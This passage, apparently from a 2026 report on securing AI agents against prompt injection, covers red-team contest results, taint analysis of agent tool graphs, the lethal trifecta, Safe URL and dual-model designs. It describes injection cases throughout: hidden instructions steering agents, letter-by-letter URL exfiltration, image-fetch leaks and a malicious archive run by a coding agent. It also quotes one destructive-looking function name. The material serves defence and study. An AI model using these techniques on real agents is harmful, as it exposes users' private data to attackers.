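These attackers had advantages that many real ones lack. They had ample computing power, and the search-based attack on the detectors received each detector's confidence score after every attempt, which someone emailing a company would not see. But a determined attacker can download an open detector, practise on it privately and send the company only the final version. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful because they are easy to install and stop some unsophisticated attacks. The rates in the table come from different benchmarks, so they can't be used to rank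 the defences.

### A public contest with 13 models

Most of those twelve defences were research prototypes or additions to a model. AI companies also build resistance into their main models, and a public contest tested 13 of these models. Gray Swan, an AI security company, ran the contest, and the UK AI Security Institute and several AI developers sponsored it. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports the results. Its co-authors include staff from companies whose models were tested.

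In one scenario, which was close to the email assistant, a user asks the agent to check urgent emails, and the attacker controls the text of a marketing email in the inbox. To succeed, the attacker must make the agent mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. A program checked whether the agent took the harmful action. In most scenarios, a language model also scored the agent's reply, because the attack counted only if the user would not notice it.

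The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts and succeeded 8,648 times. *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, an account by the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), emphasises that participants breached every model at least once, but that the models differed sharply. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

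These rates are shares of all attempts, including early drafts that participants were still improving. But Claude Opus 4.5 failed at least once in 13 of the 37 scenarios (35%), and Gemini 2.5 Pro did so in all 37. The number of successful attempts also grew roughly in proportion to the total, so participants showed no sign of running out of ideas.

General ability did not predict resistance well. The correlation between a model's score on a difficult science test and its attack success rate was weak (r = −0.31) and not statistically significant. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 both scored around 85% on the science test, yet attacks succeeded 8.5% of the time against Gemini and 4.8% against Kimi. Dziemian and colleagues attribute more of the difference to how each company trains its models. Within the Claude family, though, more capable models were more resistant.

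An attack that works on one model may also work on others. Gray Swan reran 2,679 successful attacks on all the models. The 44 that had succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 worked between 44% and 81% of the time on the other models, but none of the attacks found against Qwen3 VL worked on Opus 4.5. One template told the agent that it was inside a simulation with a special control panel. With small changes in wording, this template succeeded in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models.

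The conditions favoured the attackers in some ways, since they could read the conversation up to the injection and knew exactly which action they had to cause. But each attack had a single turn, so they could not adjust to the agent's response within a conversation. Most of the models also ran without extended thinking, in which a model writes out reasoning before it answers. Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound on single-turn vulnerability, not an estimate of how often real attacks succeed. They nonetheless conclude that training alone is not enough and call for protection in the design of the whole system. CaMeL, which keeps untrusted text out of the agent's decisions, is one example of such a design.

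### The most resistant models of 2026

The strongest evidence that models can resist attacks comes from models released after that contest. Gray Swan has since built a benchmark with 28 new scenarios and 1,130 attacks chosen because they had worked on several models. In July 2026, Anthropic reported that a single attack on Claude Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time and an attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time. The figures for its predecessor, Opus 4.8, were 0.5% and 5.5%.

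Other Claude models had rates close to Opus 5's within 15 attempts, at 2.6% for Mythos 5 and, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, 2.8% for Fable 5. The rate was 16.5% for Muse Spark, the best model from another company, and 20.0% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic tested its own models without additional safeguards and the others through their public services, which may have had additional safeguards, so the comparison does not obviously favor Claude.

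Anthropic also ran tests in which the attacker improves with experience. It used Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan, against coding agents and agents that operate a graphical interface, with 200 attempts per scenario. In the browser test, professional red-teamers had ten attempts per scenario. The table shows how many scenarios had at least one successful attack when the models used extended thinking.

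| Setting | Opus 4.8, no safeguards | Opus 5, no safeguards | Opus 5, with safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 23 of 40 | 13 of 40 | 4 of 40 |
| Graphical interface | 7 of 14 | 1 of 14 | 1 of 14 |
| Browser | 81 of 129 | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

Earlier results show how quickly this has changed. In February 2026, the technology site VentureBeat reported that attacks on Claude Opus 4.6 through a graphical interface succeeded 17.8% of the time on the first attempt without safeguards. Within 200 attempts, they succeeded 78.6% of the time without safeguards and 57.1% with them. If that test used the same 14 scenarios as the later one, attacks succeeded in 11 scenarios without safeguards and 8 with them, compared with one for Opus 5.

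Auto mode, which combines probes on incoming text with a classifier on outgoing actions, accounts for much of the browser result. Against Mythos 5, attackers breached 71 of the 129 scenarios without auto mode and none with it. Anthropic says this is because an attack must defeat both layers, which act at different points. An email that looks harmless enough to pass the probes must still produce an action that looks harmless to the classifier. Probes alone were less reliable. In the coding test, they cut the number of breached scenarios from 13 to 4 for Opus 5, but the number rose from 8 to 11 for Mythos 5.

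Even when no attack succeeds in n independent trials, the true success rate could be as high as about 3/n at the usual 95% confidence level, or 2.3% for 129 scenarios. The uncertainty about real use is larger, because this calculation assumes that the scenarios are a random sample of what a browser agent will meet, and they are not.

By December 2026, Google's models had reached similar levels. UA.News' *OpenAI and Anthropic models bypass evaluation systems less often* reports from Gray Swan's public tracker that 15 different attacks compromised Gemini 4 Argon 2.3% of the time and Gemini 4 Carbon 2.5%. Claude models were close behind. Nvidia's Nemotron 3.5 Super VL, whose weights anyone can download, was the most vulnerable at 94.3%. A company's choice of model can therefore greatly affect its exposure.

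Anthropic describes Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model to date on Gray Swan's benchmark, and OpenAI considers GPT-6 Astra significantly more robust to prompt injection than GPT-5.6 Sol. Gray Swan's tracker gives 0.8% for the newer GPT-6.2 Astra, but that figure is how often the model exploits gaps in a test to get a high score, not a measure of its robustness to prompt injection.

### From one attempt to many

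A success rate means little without the number of attempts. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent, all k of them fail with probability (1 − p)^k. The chance of at least one success is therefore

1 − (1 − p)^k.

For Claude Opus 5, p is 0.2%, so the formula gives 3.0% at k = 15, but Anthropic reports 2.0%. Reported rates are also below the formula's predictions in other tests. The figures for Opus 4.5 come from an older Gray Swan benchmark, as reported in The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

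| Model | One attempt | Attempts | Formula | Reported |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 15 | 37.6% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38.2% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99.2% | 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 17.8% | 200 | Nearly 100% | 78.6% |

The gap arises because repeated attempts at the same scenario are not independent. Some scenarios are much easier to attack than others. If the first ten attacks on a scenario fail, it is probably a hard one, so the eleventh is less likely than average to succeed.

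A made-up case comes close to the figures for Opus 5. Suppose 27 of the 28 scenarios are impossible to breach, and attacks on the remaining one succeed 5.6% of the time. The average success rate for a single attempt is then 5.6% / 28, or 0.2%. Within 15 attempts, the attacker has a 58% chance of breaching the weak scenario, so the average over all 28 is 2.1%. The real distribution may be quite different, but an average this low is compatible with one scenario that is breached more often than not within 15 attempts.

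Anthropic's coding test has the same pattern. Attacks on Opus 5 without safeguards succeeded in 0.56% of attempts. If all 40 scenarios had been equally difficult, 200 attempts at each should have breached about 27. They breached 13, so successes were concentrated in a minority of scenarios. For a developer, the average is therefore less useful than knowing whether the application resembles one of the scenarios that were breached.

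An attacker can also send one attack to many targets instead of repeatedly attacking the same one. If someone sends an email to 10,000 assistants and each has a 0.2% chance of obeying it, the expected number of successes is 20, whether or not the outcomes are independent. Real emails may succeed less often than attacks that researchers selected for their strength, but they cost very little to send.

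### What fixed test sets can show

A fixed set of attacks lets developers compare how well two models resist the same texts, or one model before and after a change. A failure reveals a real weakness in a defence, but Nasr and colleagues argue that a pass doesn't show the defence is secure. For example, Spotlighting stopped almost all of AgentDojo's standard attacks but failed against attacks found by a search that took the defence into account.

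Fixed test sets also become less useful over time. Zou's *Current State of AI Agent Security* describes an earlier Gray Swan contest in which participants eventually breached every agent and caused 60,000 violations of the agents' rules. Anthropic used Gray Swan's Agent Red Teaming benchmark until its models had scored at or near the maximum for several releases, then replaced it with the current benchmark.

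Results for coding agents also changed with the test. In February 2026, Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attack attempts in a constrained coding environment. In the July test, Shade breached Opus 4.8, a later model, in 23 of 40 coding scenarios with extended thinking and 38 of 40 without it. The February result does not guarantee resistance to other attacks or in other environments.

The source of the attacks matters as much as their number. The attacks in Gray Swan's benchmark come from a contest against other models, so the 2.0% for Opus 5 is the success rate of attacks that were not developed against it. In the contest that Dziemian and colleagues studied, the full collection of attacks developed against other models worked on Claude Opus 4.5 only 2.5% of the time. But attacks that participants had developed against Claude and GPT models worked at least half the time when Gray Swan repeated them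 on the model they were developed against. Shade, Gray Swan's tool, had practised on the same coding scenarios with earlier models, so its attacks on Opus 5 in those scenarios were also partly developed against other models.

Most benchmarks also use a single message, but some attackers can send several. SC Media's *Cisco study finds major frontier models susceptible to multi-turn prompt injection attacks* reports Cisco's tests of 15 models. The attack success rate rose from 2.7% with single messages to 24.7% over several turns against GPT-5.4, and from 3.6% to 16.2% against Claude Opus 4.6. It fell from 64.9% to 30.9% against Amazon's Nova Micro, so multi-turn rates can't be estimated by scaling up single-turn ones. Cisco's categories include hate speech and specialised advice, so many of these attacks are closer to jailbreaks than to instructions hidden in an email. But an email attacker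 can also follow up if the assistant replies to the first message.

AI companies also publish results from different tests, so buyers can't compare them directly. VentureBeat compared the companies' safety documents and found that Anthropic reported results for Opus 4.8 from its own browser test and Gray Swan's tools, while OpenAI used an internal evaluation of connected services for GPT-5.5.

CAISI favours repeated contests with new scenarios and current models, as do Dziemian and colleagues, and Gray Swan plans to update its benchmark every quarter. Anthropic has also used bug bounties, which pay outsiders to attack its latest model directly. When it published the results for Opus 5 in July, it was still setting up the bounty for that model.

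## Tracing what untrusted input can reach

The damage from a successful attack depends on what the agent can do after it has processed the attacker's text, however rarely attacks succeed. An engineer can work this out from the application's design. The method, called taint analysis, is older than language models. Security analysts have long used it to trace how a value typed into a web form travels through a program to a database command.

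### The procedure

For an agent, the analysis has five steps:

1. List the sources. Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, count any tool whose output may contain an attacker's text, including one that retrieves stored memories.
2. List the sinks, such as sending email or running code.
3. Draw a directed graph, with a point for each component and an arrow wherever one component's output can become another's input.
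4. Find every path that leads from a source to a sink.
5. Break each path by removing an arrow or putting a check on it.

In symbols, let V be the set of components, E the arrows between them, S the sources, T the sinks, and K the arrows that carry an approved check. The requirement is that

for every s in S and every t in T, the graph (V, E ∖ K) contains no path from s to t.

No path may lead from a source to a sink without an approved check. A program can test this by deleting the checked arrows and following the remaining ones from each source. The search is quick even for a large application, but its result depends on the accuracy of the lists. If the engineer forgets an arrow, the application can pass the test and still be open to attack.

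The organisation also has to decide which checks to approve. A fixed list of recipients in the harness is a deterministic check. Classifiers and people clicking "allow" sometimes make mistakes, so an organisation that approves either as a check accepts its error rate on that path.

Several tools automate parts of the procedure. Invariant Labs (2025), the research division of the security company Snyk, introduced toxic flow analysis, which builds a graph of the order in which an agent could use its tools. It marks each tool by how trustworthy its content is, how sensitive its data is and whether it could send data out, then scores the dangerous sequences. The technology consultancy Thoughtworks considers the technique promising but in its early stages. *AgentLens* (2026) adds known weaknesses and existing guardrails to the graph, then uses the paths to build multi-step test attacks.

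### The email assistant as a graph

Everything the email assistant's tools return goes into the context window, and the model can then call any of the four tools. The context window is therefore in the middle of the graph.

| Component | Sends its output to | Source? | Sink? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inbox search | Context window | Yes, anyone can email the user | No |
| Staff records | Context window | Yes, employees edit their own job descriptions | No |
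| Web fetch | Context window and the site it contacts | Yes, anyone can publish a page | Yes, the requested address can carry data |
| Mail tool | Recipients' inboxes | No | Yes, it can send private data or a phishing link |
| Context window and model | All four tools | No | No |

Three sources and two sinks make six paths, all of which pass through the model. Guarding the two sinks takes fewer checks than closing the three sources, and the assistant can still read mail from strangers.

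Suppose the harness refuses to send mail to any address that is not on the company's list of known recipients. The table shows how this changes what a malicious email could cause.

| Action | Any recipient allowed | Known recipients only |
|---|---|---|
| Email a staff record to the attacker | Possible | Blocked |
| Put a staff record in a web address and fetch it | Possible | Possible |
| Email a colleague a phishing link in the user's name | Possible | Possible |
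| Email a colleague text that steers the colleague's own assistant | Possible | Possible |

The application still fails the requirement because the web tool has no check and needs its own. For mail to colleagues, the harness could strip out links and images or hold the message until the user approves it. Plain-text instructions could still steer a colleague's assistant if the user missed them when approving the message.

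The limit also depends on how a recipient becomes known. If the harness accepts anyone who has previously written to the user, the attacker qualifies by sending the malicious email. Untrusted input must not be able to reach the list of known recipients, so the assistant must not be able to add entries to it. The user therefore has to add the caterer by hand before the assistant can reply.

Even the user's own address can be an unsafe destination. Willison (2026) describes a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which could email the user without approval and include images from outside websites. When the user opened such a message, the mail program requested the images, and those requests could send an attacker a link for downloading the user's files. A graph that stops at the mail tool would omit the last step of this path, from the user's mail program to the attacker's server.

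Developers usually have to write the recipient check themselves. An audit of three agent frameworks found that all of them control which tools an agent can use, but none checks the values passed to a tool by default (*Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, 2026). An agent with permission to send mail can therefore send it to anyone.

### Why the model joins everything in its context

In ordinary code, an analyst can follow a value from line to line. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026) compares three tools that contain the same operation for running a command. The first passes the agent's input straight to the command. The second overwrites the input with a fixed value, so the agent has no influence. The third accepts the input only if it is on a list of permitted commands. Searching only for the dangerous operation would not distinguish between them.

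The model connects the email assistant's inbox to its mail tool while it runs. This connection appears nowhere in the code and may leave no visible trace. In one of Cai and colleagues' test cases, a web page contained hidden instructions for a research agent to include a confidential patient note in its memo, but in its own words, which left no original phrase for a filter to match. In another, a poisoned search result contained an announcement of a new company procedure, and the agent called a different tool than usual. The attacker's text affected the choice of tool, so it didn't need to appear in what the agent sent.

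It is therefore safest to assume that anything in the context window can influence every tool the agent has. Invariant Labs argues that a security review has to consider every possible combination of tools, which means 16 combinations for the email assistant's four tools and 1,024 for ten. Reviewers don't have to list these combinations if they use a graph that connects all the tools through the model. Any path that exists with fewer tools is also in the full graph, so one search of that graph covers every combination.

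This assumption overstates the danger because it covers everything that could happen, however rarely. A research agent that reads web pages and writes reports has a path from source to sink on every run, including the harmless ones. An alarm raised each time the agent used this path would nearly always be false.

Cai and colleagues measured the benefit of tracing what influenced an agent's action. Their tool, NeuroTaint, examines the log of a finished run for similar meaning between source and sink, and tests whether the agent would still have taken the action if the suspicious text had been replaced. On 400 scenarios, 92.1% of the flows it flagged were real, and it found 93.5% of the real ones. Its F1 score, which combines these two measures, was 0.928, against 0.522 for FIDES, which labels data by origin. Cai and colleagues built the benchmark themselves, around the kinds of flow that NeuroTaint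 is designed to find. NeuroTaint also needs a log, so it can't replace an analysis done before the agent runs.

*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (2026) narrows the assumption earlier, at each call to a model, by predicting whether attacker-controlled text can pass through the model's answer to a particular dangerous operation. For example, an attacker may be able to change a yes-or-no answer but can't fit a command into it.

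Some agents with an open path have resisted many attacks. Willison (2026) reports on a public challenge in which Fernando Irarrázaval invited people to email his assistant and try to extract a secret. The assistant ran on OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, with Claude Opus 4.6 as the model and a short list of things it must never do because of an email. After 6,000 attempts, nobody had obtained the secret. But the same model did much worse in Anthropic's graphical-interface tests, so the result is weak evidence of how it would perform in other settings or against more practised attackers.

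*The Framing Gap* (2026) found a similar difference between a model and a finished product. Attacks that made a model leak a secret up to 100% of the time through OpenAI's API failed in all 48 valid trials in ChatGPT. The experimenters could not observe ChatGPT's internal checks and did not attribute the difference to any one of them. An outsider who drew ChatGPT's graph from its visible tools could easily leave out a check that was stopping these attacks.

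### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Most people who connect tools to an agent will never draw a graph, but two well-known rules reduce the same test to three questions about the whole agent.

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) warns against giving an agent access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally all at once. An attacker could then plant instructions in the untrusted content that lead the agent to send out the private data. A single connection can provide all three. For example, GitHub's official tool server let an agent read public issues that an attacker could have written, read private code and publish changes that could contain that code.

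Willison aimed the warning partly at users. A company can close a leak in its own product, but it can't control what happens when a user combines that product with tools from elsewhere. He advises these users to avoid the combination entirely, because he doesn't trust products that claim to catch most attacks.

Meta turned this idea into a design rule, also inspired by a similar rule for Google's Chromium browser. Until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in a session:

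- **[A]** It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **[B]** It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **[C]** It can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three in one session should be supervised, either through human approval of its actions or another reliable form of validation.

Meta's Email-Bot could follow the rule in three ways. To keep only access to private data [B] and external actions [C], it would read mail only from trusted senders, which removes the sources of untrusted input. To keep only untrusted input [A] and external actions [C], it would run in a test environment without real data. To keep only [A] and [B], it would send mail only to trusted recipients or after a person had checked the draft, so each path to the mail tool would have a check.

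Properties can also change during a session. An agent might begin with web access but no private data, then lose the ability to communicate externally before it opens internal systems. An attacker's text may still be in its context window, but the agent can no longer send anything out. Communication has to stay off for the rest of the session, because restoring it would let the attacker's text direct the agent to send out private data.

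Both rules are much easier to apply than a graph, but less precise. The email assistant still has all three properties after the company limits outgoing mail, because it can still fetch any web address. The graph shows that one route to the attacker has closed and another remains.

### Harms that the two rules leave out

The trifecta tests for data theft, but an email that makes an assistant delete messages or cancel an order may do serious harm without any private data leaving the company. Willison (2025) acknowledged this gap in *New prompt injection papers* and welcomed Meta's rule because its property [C] includes changes of state.

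In an update to the same post, he objected to Meta's diagram labelling [A] and [C] together as safe, because text from an attacker could still trigger a harmful change even if the agent had no private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that [B] covers access to any sensitive system, whether or not it holds private data. An agent without [B] can act freely only where nothing important is at stake, such as in a tightly closed test environment. Meta also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

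Ayzenberg's reply answers the objection, but it makes the number of properties an agent has depend on what the developer considers sensitive. Suppose an agent reads web pages and sends mail from a company account that contains no messages. A phishing message from that account could do real damage, so on Ayzenberg's reading the account is a sensitive system and the agent has all three properties. A developer who thinks only of private data would count two for the same agent.

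Neither rule prevents false answers. In Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), testers used a web page and a PDF to make a browsing agent claim that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the moon. They also made it recommend a fictitious company. The sink was the user's screen, so the attack did not need to send any data out. Meta lists misinformation in an agent's response among the lesser harms that its rule does not address, along with ordinary mistakes and excessive privileges. For an agent that gives medical or financial advice, a false answer may be the most serious harm.

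A rule that examines one session at a time can miss attacks that pass through memory. A stranger's document can cause the agent to save a note during a session without private data. The agent can then load that note in a later session that has private data and a mail tool but no obvious untrusted input. Each session appears to have two properties, yet the stranger's text can reach the mail tool. The rule catches this only if it counts saved notes as untrusted input. The graph shows the memory store as one component with arrows into and out of it, so the path is visible no matter how far apart the sessions are.

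### Source-sink analysis in ChatGPT and Safe URL

OpenAI uses source-sink analysis to decide where ChatGPT needs a check. In most attacks OpenAI sees, the attacker tries to persuade ChatGPT to send secret information from a conversation to a third party. Any outside text can be the source, and blocking all such text would prevent ChatGPT from using the web. OpenAI therefore concentrates on the sink, where the information is transmitted, and aims to keep sensitive information from leaving silently.

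Web addresses are a convenient way out, as in the SpAIware attack, where the app leaked the user's messages by fetching an image.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains the check, called Safe URL:

1. OpenAI runs a crawler that records addresses it finds on the public web. The crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When an agent is about to fetch an address automatically, the software checks whether exactly that address is in the crawler's index.
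3. If it is, the agent loads the page or image.
4. If it is not, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning before anything opens.

The reasoning is that an address that was already public, independently of any conversation, is unlikely to contain that conversation's secrets. An address the model has just assembled on an attacker's instructions would normally be missing from the index. The warning is titled "Check this link is safe" and states that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation. It shows the full address, with options to copy or open the link. The same mechanism covers OpenAI's Atlas browser and its Deep Research feature.

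OpenAI decided against relying on a list of well-known sites. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a trusted address can lead to an attacker's server. A strict list would also produce frequent warnings, which people learn to click through. An attacker may also have an account on a trusted site. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, could contact only certain domains, including Anthropic's own. Willison reports that the security company Prompt Armor got the agent to upload a user's files to Anthropic using an attacker's account key.

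An exact match still leaves a narrower leak. Rehberger points out in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that an attacker can prepare 36 public pages, one for each letter and digit, and wait for the crawler to index them. Hidden instructions then tell the model to spell out a secret by visiting the pages in order. Every address is public, but the sequence of visits is private. With N indexed pages to choose from, each visit can reveal up to

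log₂ N bits.

Each visit leaks about 5.2 bits with 36 pages and 12 bits with 4,096. A long document would take many visits, but a five-letter name would take only five with 36 pages. OpenAI acknowledges this kind of leak in its technical paper. Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, which would make the attack harder but not stop it completely.

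A different check had the same weakness. Anthropic let Claude's web tool visit only addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned, plus links on pages it had already fetched. According to Willison, Ayush Paul used the permission to follow links to lead Claude through a site letter by letter, and obtained a user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then removed that permission. If the email assistant's web tool followed this stricter rule, an incoming email could no longer make it fetch an address containing a staff record.

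Safe URL protects against data leaking unnoticed through the URL itself. OpenAI says it does not establish that a page is truthful or free of malicious instructions. A page could still make ChatGPT give a false answer or save a misleading note. The check works only where developers have installed it, and the Mac app originally lacked an earlier version of it.

Attackers can exploit one overlooked sink even if a team has analyzed the others carefully. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested an agent that automatically previewed web addresses. Attackers could make it send an unintended request with a probability of about 0.89, while the user saw a normal reply. Safety checks on the agent's replies missed 95% of the successful attacks. A team could easily leave link previews off its list of sinks because they look like part of the display.

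### Finding the paths in an application's own code

Searching the code can reveal forgotten sinks. *Agent Audit* (2026) describes a program that traces data through an agent's Python code and checks the agent's passwords and permission settings. On 22 samples containing 42 known vulnerabilities, it found 40 and raised six false alarms. The program relies on analysis rules and took less than a second per scan.

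Cui ran a similar analysis on 67 real agent projects and found 23,866 operations that might be sensitive. The program found evidence that input could influence 41% of them, and a visible safeguard for 13%. Cui also examined 22 behaviours closely enough to reproduce them. Twenty had adequate safeguards under the conditions tested, one was a confirmed vulnerability and one was awaiting disclosure. The 22 were not a random sample, so they can't show how many of the other operations are dangerous.

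Skill files are reusable instructions for an agent. *Can Agents Trust Their Skills?* (2026) found 1,566 paths from skill files to sensitive operations in 11 agents, then ran test attacks to determine which paths an attacker could use.

*Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026) notes that existing analysis rules for JavaScript and TypeScript mostly follow data from a web request to an operation such as a database query. They do not follow data into an agent's prompt, through the model and out to a tool. The analysis also needs some facts that are not in the code, such as how a company has configured the agent.

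A long-context model could help because it can read code, documentation and settings together and recognise an unfamiliar sink from its purpose. So far, the evidence favours combining models with conventional analysis. *Argus* (2026) found that a model could not trace the data behind each sink in one pass, so it used CodeQL, a code-search program, to find candidate paths and a model to review them. In *Bridging Code Property Graphs and Language Models for Program Analysis* (2026), an agent examined a codebase with 8,667 functions. Reading all the files would have exceeded its token limit, so it queried a graph of the code and read only the relevant parts.

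How well an agent finds bugs depends heavily on the model. *Can Open-Source LLM Agents Replace Static Application Security Testing Tools?* (2026) tested models on a local server and found very low accuracy and many false alarms. The strongest models do far better. In November 2026, Help Net Security reported Anthropic's results on 1,829 previously published vulnerabilities. Claude Mythos 5.2 rediscovered 89.6% and missed about 190, while Claude Opus 5.5 rediscovered 81.3% and missed about 342.

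Those figures cover software vulnerabilities in general, so they do not show what share of an agent's source-to-sink paths a model would find. Many of these paths contain no bug, only a risky combination of tools that each work as intended.

The rediscovery figures also leave out false alarms. Schneier on Security's *Mythos and Cybersecurity* cites research in which models that detected nearly every real bug also reported plausible but false ones in code that was already correct. The severity ratings need checking too. Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked* reports mismatched ratings for 14 of 27 findings, 13 of them too high. Severity often depends on how a company deploys the software, which is hard to tell from the code.

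In reach analysis, a missed path is usually worse than a false one because it leaves an opening that everyone believes is closed, whereas a false path may only lead to an unnecessary check. It makes sense to have a model propose sources, sinks and arrows, have people correct them, and have an ordinary program search for paths.

### Agents that need all three properties

The main objection to limiting reach is that the most useful agents need private data, outside content and the ability to act. For example, *ASTELD* (2026) cites a Microsoft analysis that found all three trifecta properties built into OpenClaw's design. People install OpenClaw because it can read their messages, use their files and carry out tasks. Willison noted that it had more than 114,000 GitHub stars, a rough measure of popularity, when it was two months old.

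Supporters of limits concede part of this. Meta expects that some sought-after uses will be hard to fit within its rule, such as background agents, where asking a person for approval is disruptive or ineffective. The Frontier Model Forum likewise advises deployers to weigh lost usefulness against added security.

The graph requirement is less restrictive than a ban on the combination because each path needs only a check. With checks on addresses and recipients, the email assistant can still read a stranger's message, look up a colleague and send that colleague a reply, but it needs approval to write to new contacts or open unfamiliar links. That may be tolerable when the user is at a desk, but it would defeat most of the purpose of a sales agent that contacts hundreds of new people overnight.

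Approval is also a weak check when people give it too readily. Anthropic tested 1,053 paid developers by replacing one permission request in a coding session with a clearly dangerous command. Willison reports that only 13.6% of them refused it, while Claude Code's auto mode would have blocked 89%. On this evidence, an automatic check can work better than human approval, although it would still have let through 11% of the commands.

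Anthropic has argued that better judgement can make the combination safe enough to use. Trajectory Labs, an outside tester, made 720 prompt injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. Thariq Shihipar of Anthropic said the company should have called its announcement "defeating the lethal trifecta". Willison wanted more independent confirmation, since a project's instructions could include installing a malicious package as a normal step in running its tests.

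Later that month, Rehberger reported an attack on Claude Opus 5 in auto mode that he said worked 80% of the time. Claude Code downloaded and unpacked an archive, then ran ordinary code that loaded a malicious file from it. In a few runs, Claude detected the malicious process and tried to stop it, but auto mode blocked the command. One reader pointed out that this was not a classic prompt injection, because the model never followed a hidden instruction. A reach analysis would still have included the path, because the agent could download files from strangers and run code on the same computer.

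Rehberger concluded that unattended coding agents should run in a sandbox with restricted network access and no valuable credentials. ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode similarly limits outgoing requests that could carry data to an attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, recommends it for people at elevated risk but says it isn't meant for everyone because it makes ChatGPT less useful.

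## Keeping untrusted text out of the agent's decisions

In the email assistant's graph, every path from a source to a sink runs through one model, which reads strangers' emails and also chooses the next tool. A developer can separate these two jobs so that the model that chooses the tools never reads the emails, and therefore no email can cause it to take an extra action. The agent then has control-flow integrity, which means that the user's request and other trusted information determine every course of action it could take.

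Unlike the Rule of Two, this approach lets an agent combine private data, outside content and external actions in one session, but the agent has to choose its actions without seeing the text they depend on.

### The dual-model pattern

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed using two language models. The planner, which he calls the privileged model, takes the user's request and can use tools. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools, and the design assumes that an attacker may control whatever it writes. The harness passes material between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the run goes like this:

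1. The harness gives the request to the planner.
2. The planner asks for the latest email and for the result to be stored under the name $VAR1.
3. The harness fetches the email and stores it. The planner learns only that $VAR1 now exists.
4. The planner asks for a summary of $VAR1. The harness inserts the email's text, runs the quarantined model and stores the answer as $VAR2.
5. The planner writes a reply that contains the name $VAR2, and the harness puts in the summary when it displays the reply to the user.

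An email containing an instruction to delete the inbox can corrupt the summary, but the quarantined model can't delete anything and the instruction never reaches the planner. Willison allows one exception to this separation. If the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed set of categories, the harness can check that the answer is in the set and pass it to the planner, because a predefined label such as "invoice" can't contain an attacker's instruction.

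Some designs called "dual-LLM" offer weaker protection. *ORBIT* (2026), a framework for testing multi-agent systems, includes a "dual-LLM" defence in which the quarantined model summarises each tool result and the planner reads the summary. The quarantined model is instructed not to reproduce anything that looks like a directive. If an attacker gets it to do so anyway, the directive reaches the planner, which can call tools. Buyers of a two-model product should therefore ask whether the planner ever reads text written by the quarantined model.

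Willison described his own proposal as "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and the protection fails if a single programming mistake lets untrusted text reach the planner.

### Six patterns and what they give up

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees with current kinds of language models. They ask instead which useful agents developers can protect today. Their rule is that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action with harmful side effects. They describe six patterns that apply this rule to different degrees.

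| Pattern | How it works | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | The model turns a request into one of several predefined actions and never sees the results | The agent can't use anything its tools return |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes a list of tool calls before it reads any outside data | The agent can't add a step after reading, and an attacker can still alter what a call contains |
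| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | The task has to divide neatly by document |
| Dual model | A planner handles the quarantined model's answers by name only | The planner can't reason about the content |
| Code-then-execute | The planner writes a whole program that calls tools and quarantined models | The program has to anticipate what the data will require |
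| Context minimisation | The harness removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | The model can't refer back to the user's wording |

Suppose an agent has to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounts department. With map-reduce, a separate model checks each file to see whether it is an invoice. An attacker can get a malicious file included, but could have done the same by sending a real invoice. Context minimisation guards against a different attacker, such as a customer who tries to persuade a car dealer's chatbot to give a discount. The chatbot turns the request into a database query, and the harness deletes the customer's words from the context before the model presents the results.

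Restricting a model's answer provides more safety when the restriction is tighter. For a coding agent, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a quarantined model convert outside documentation into a formal description, with function names of at most 30 characters. In a commentary that shares the paper's title, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) wondered whether an attacker could do damage even within that limit, with a name like `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance()`.

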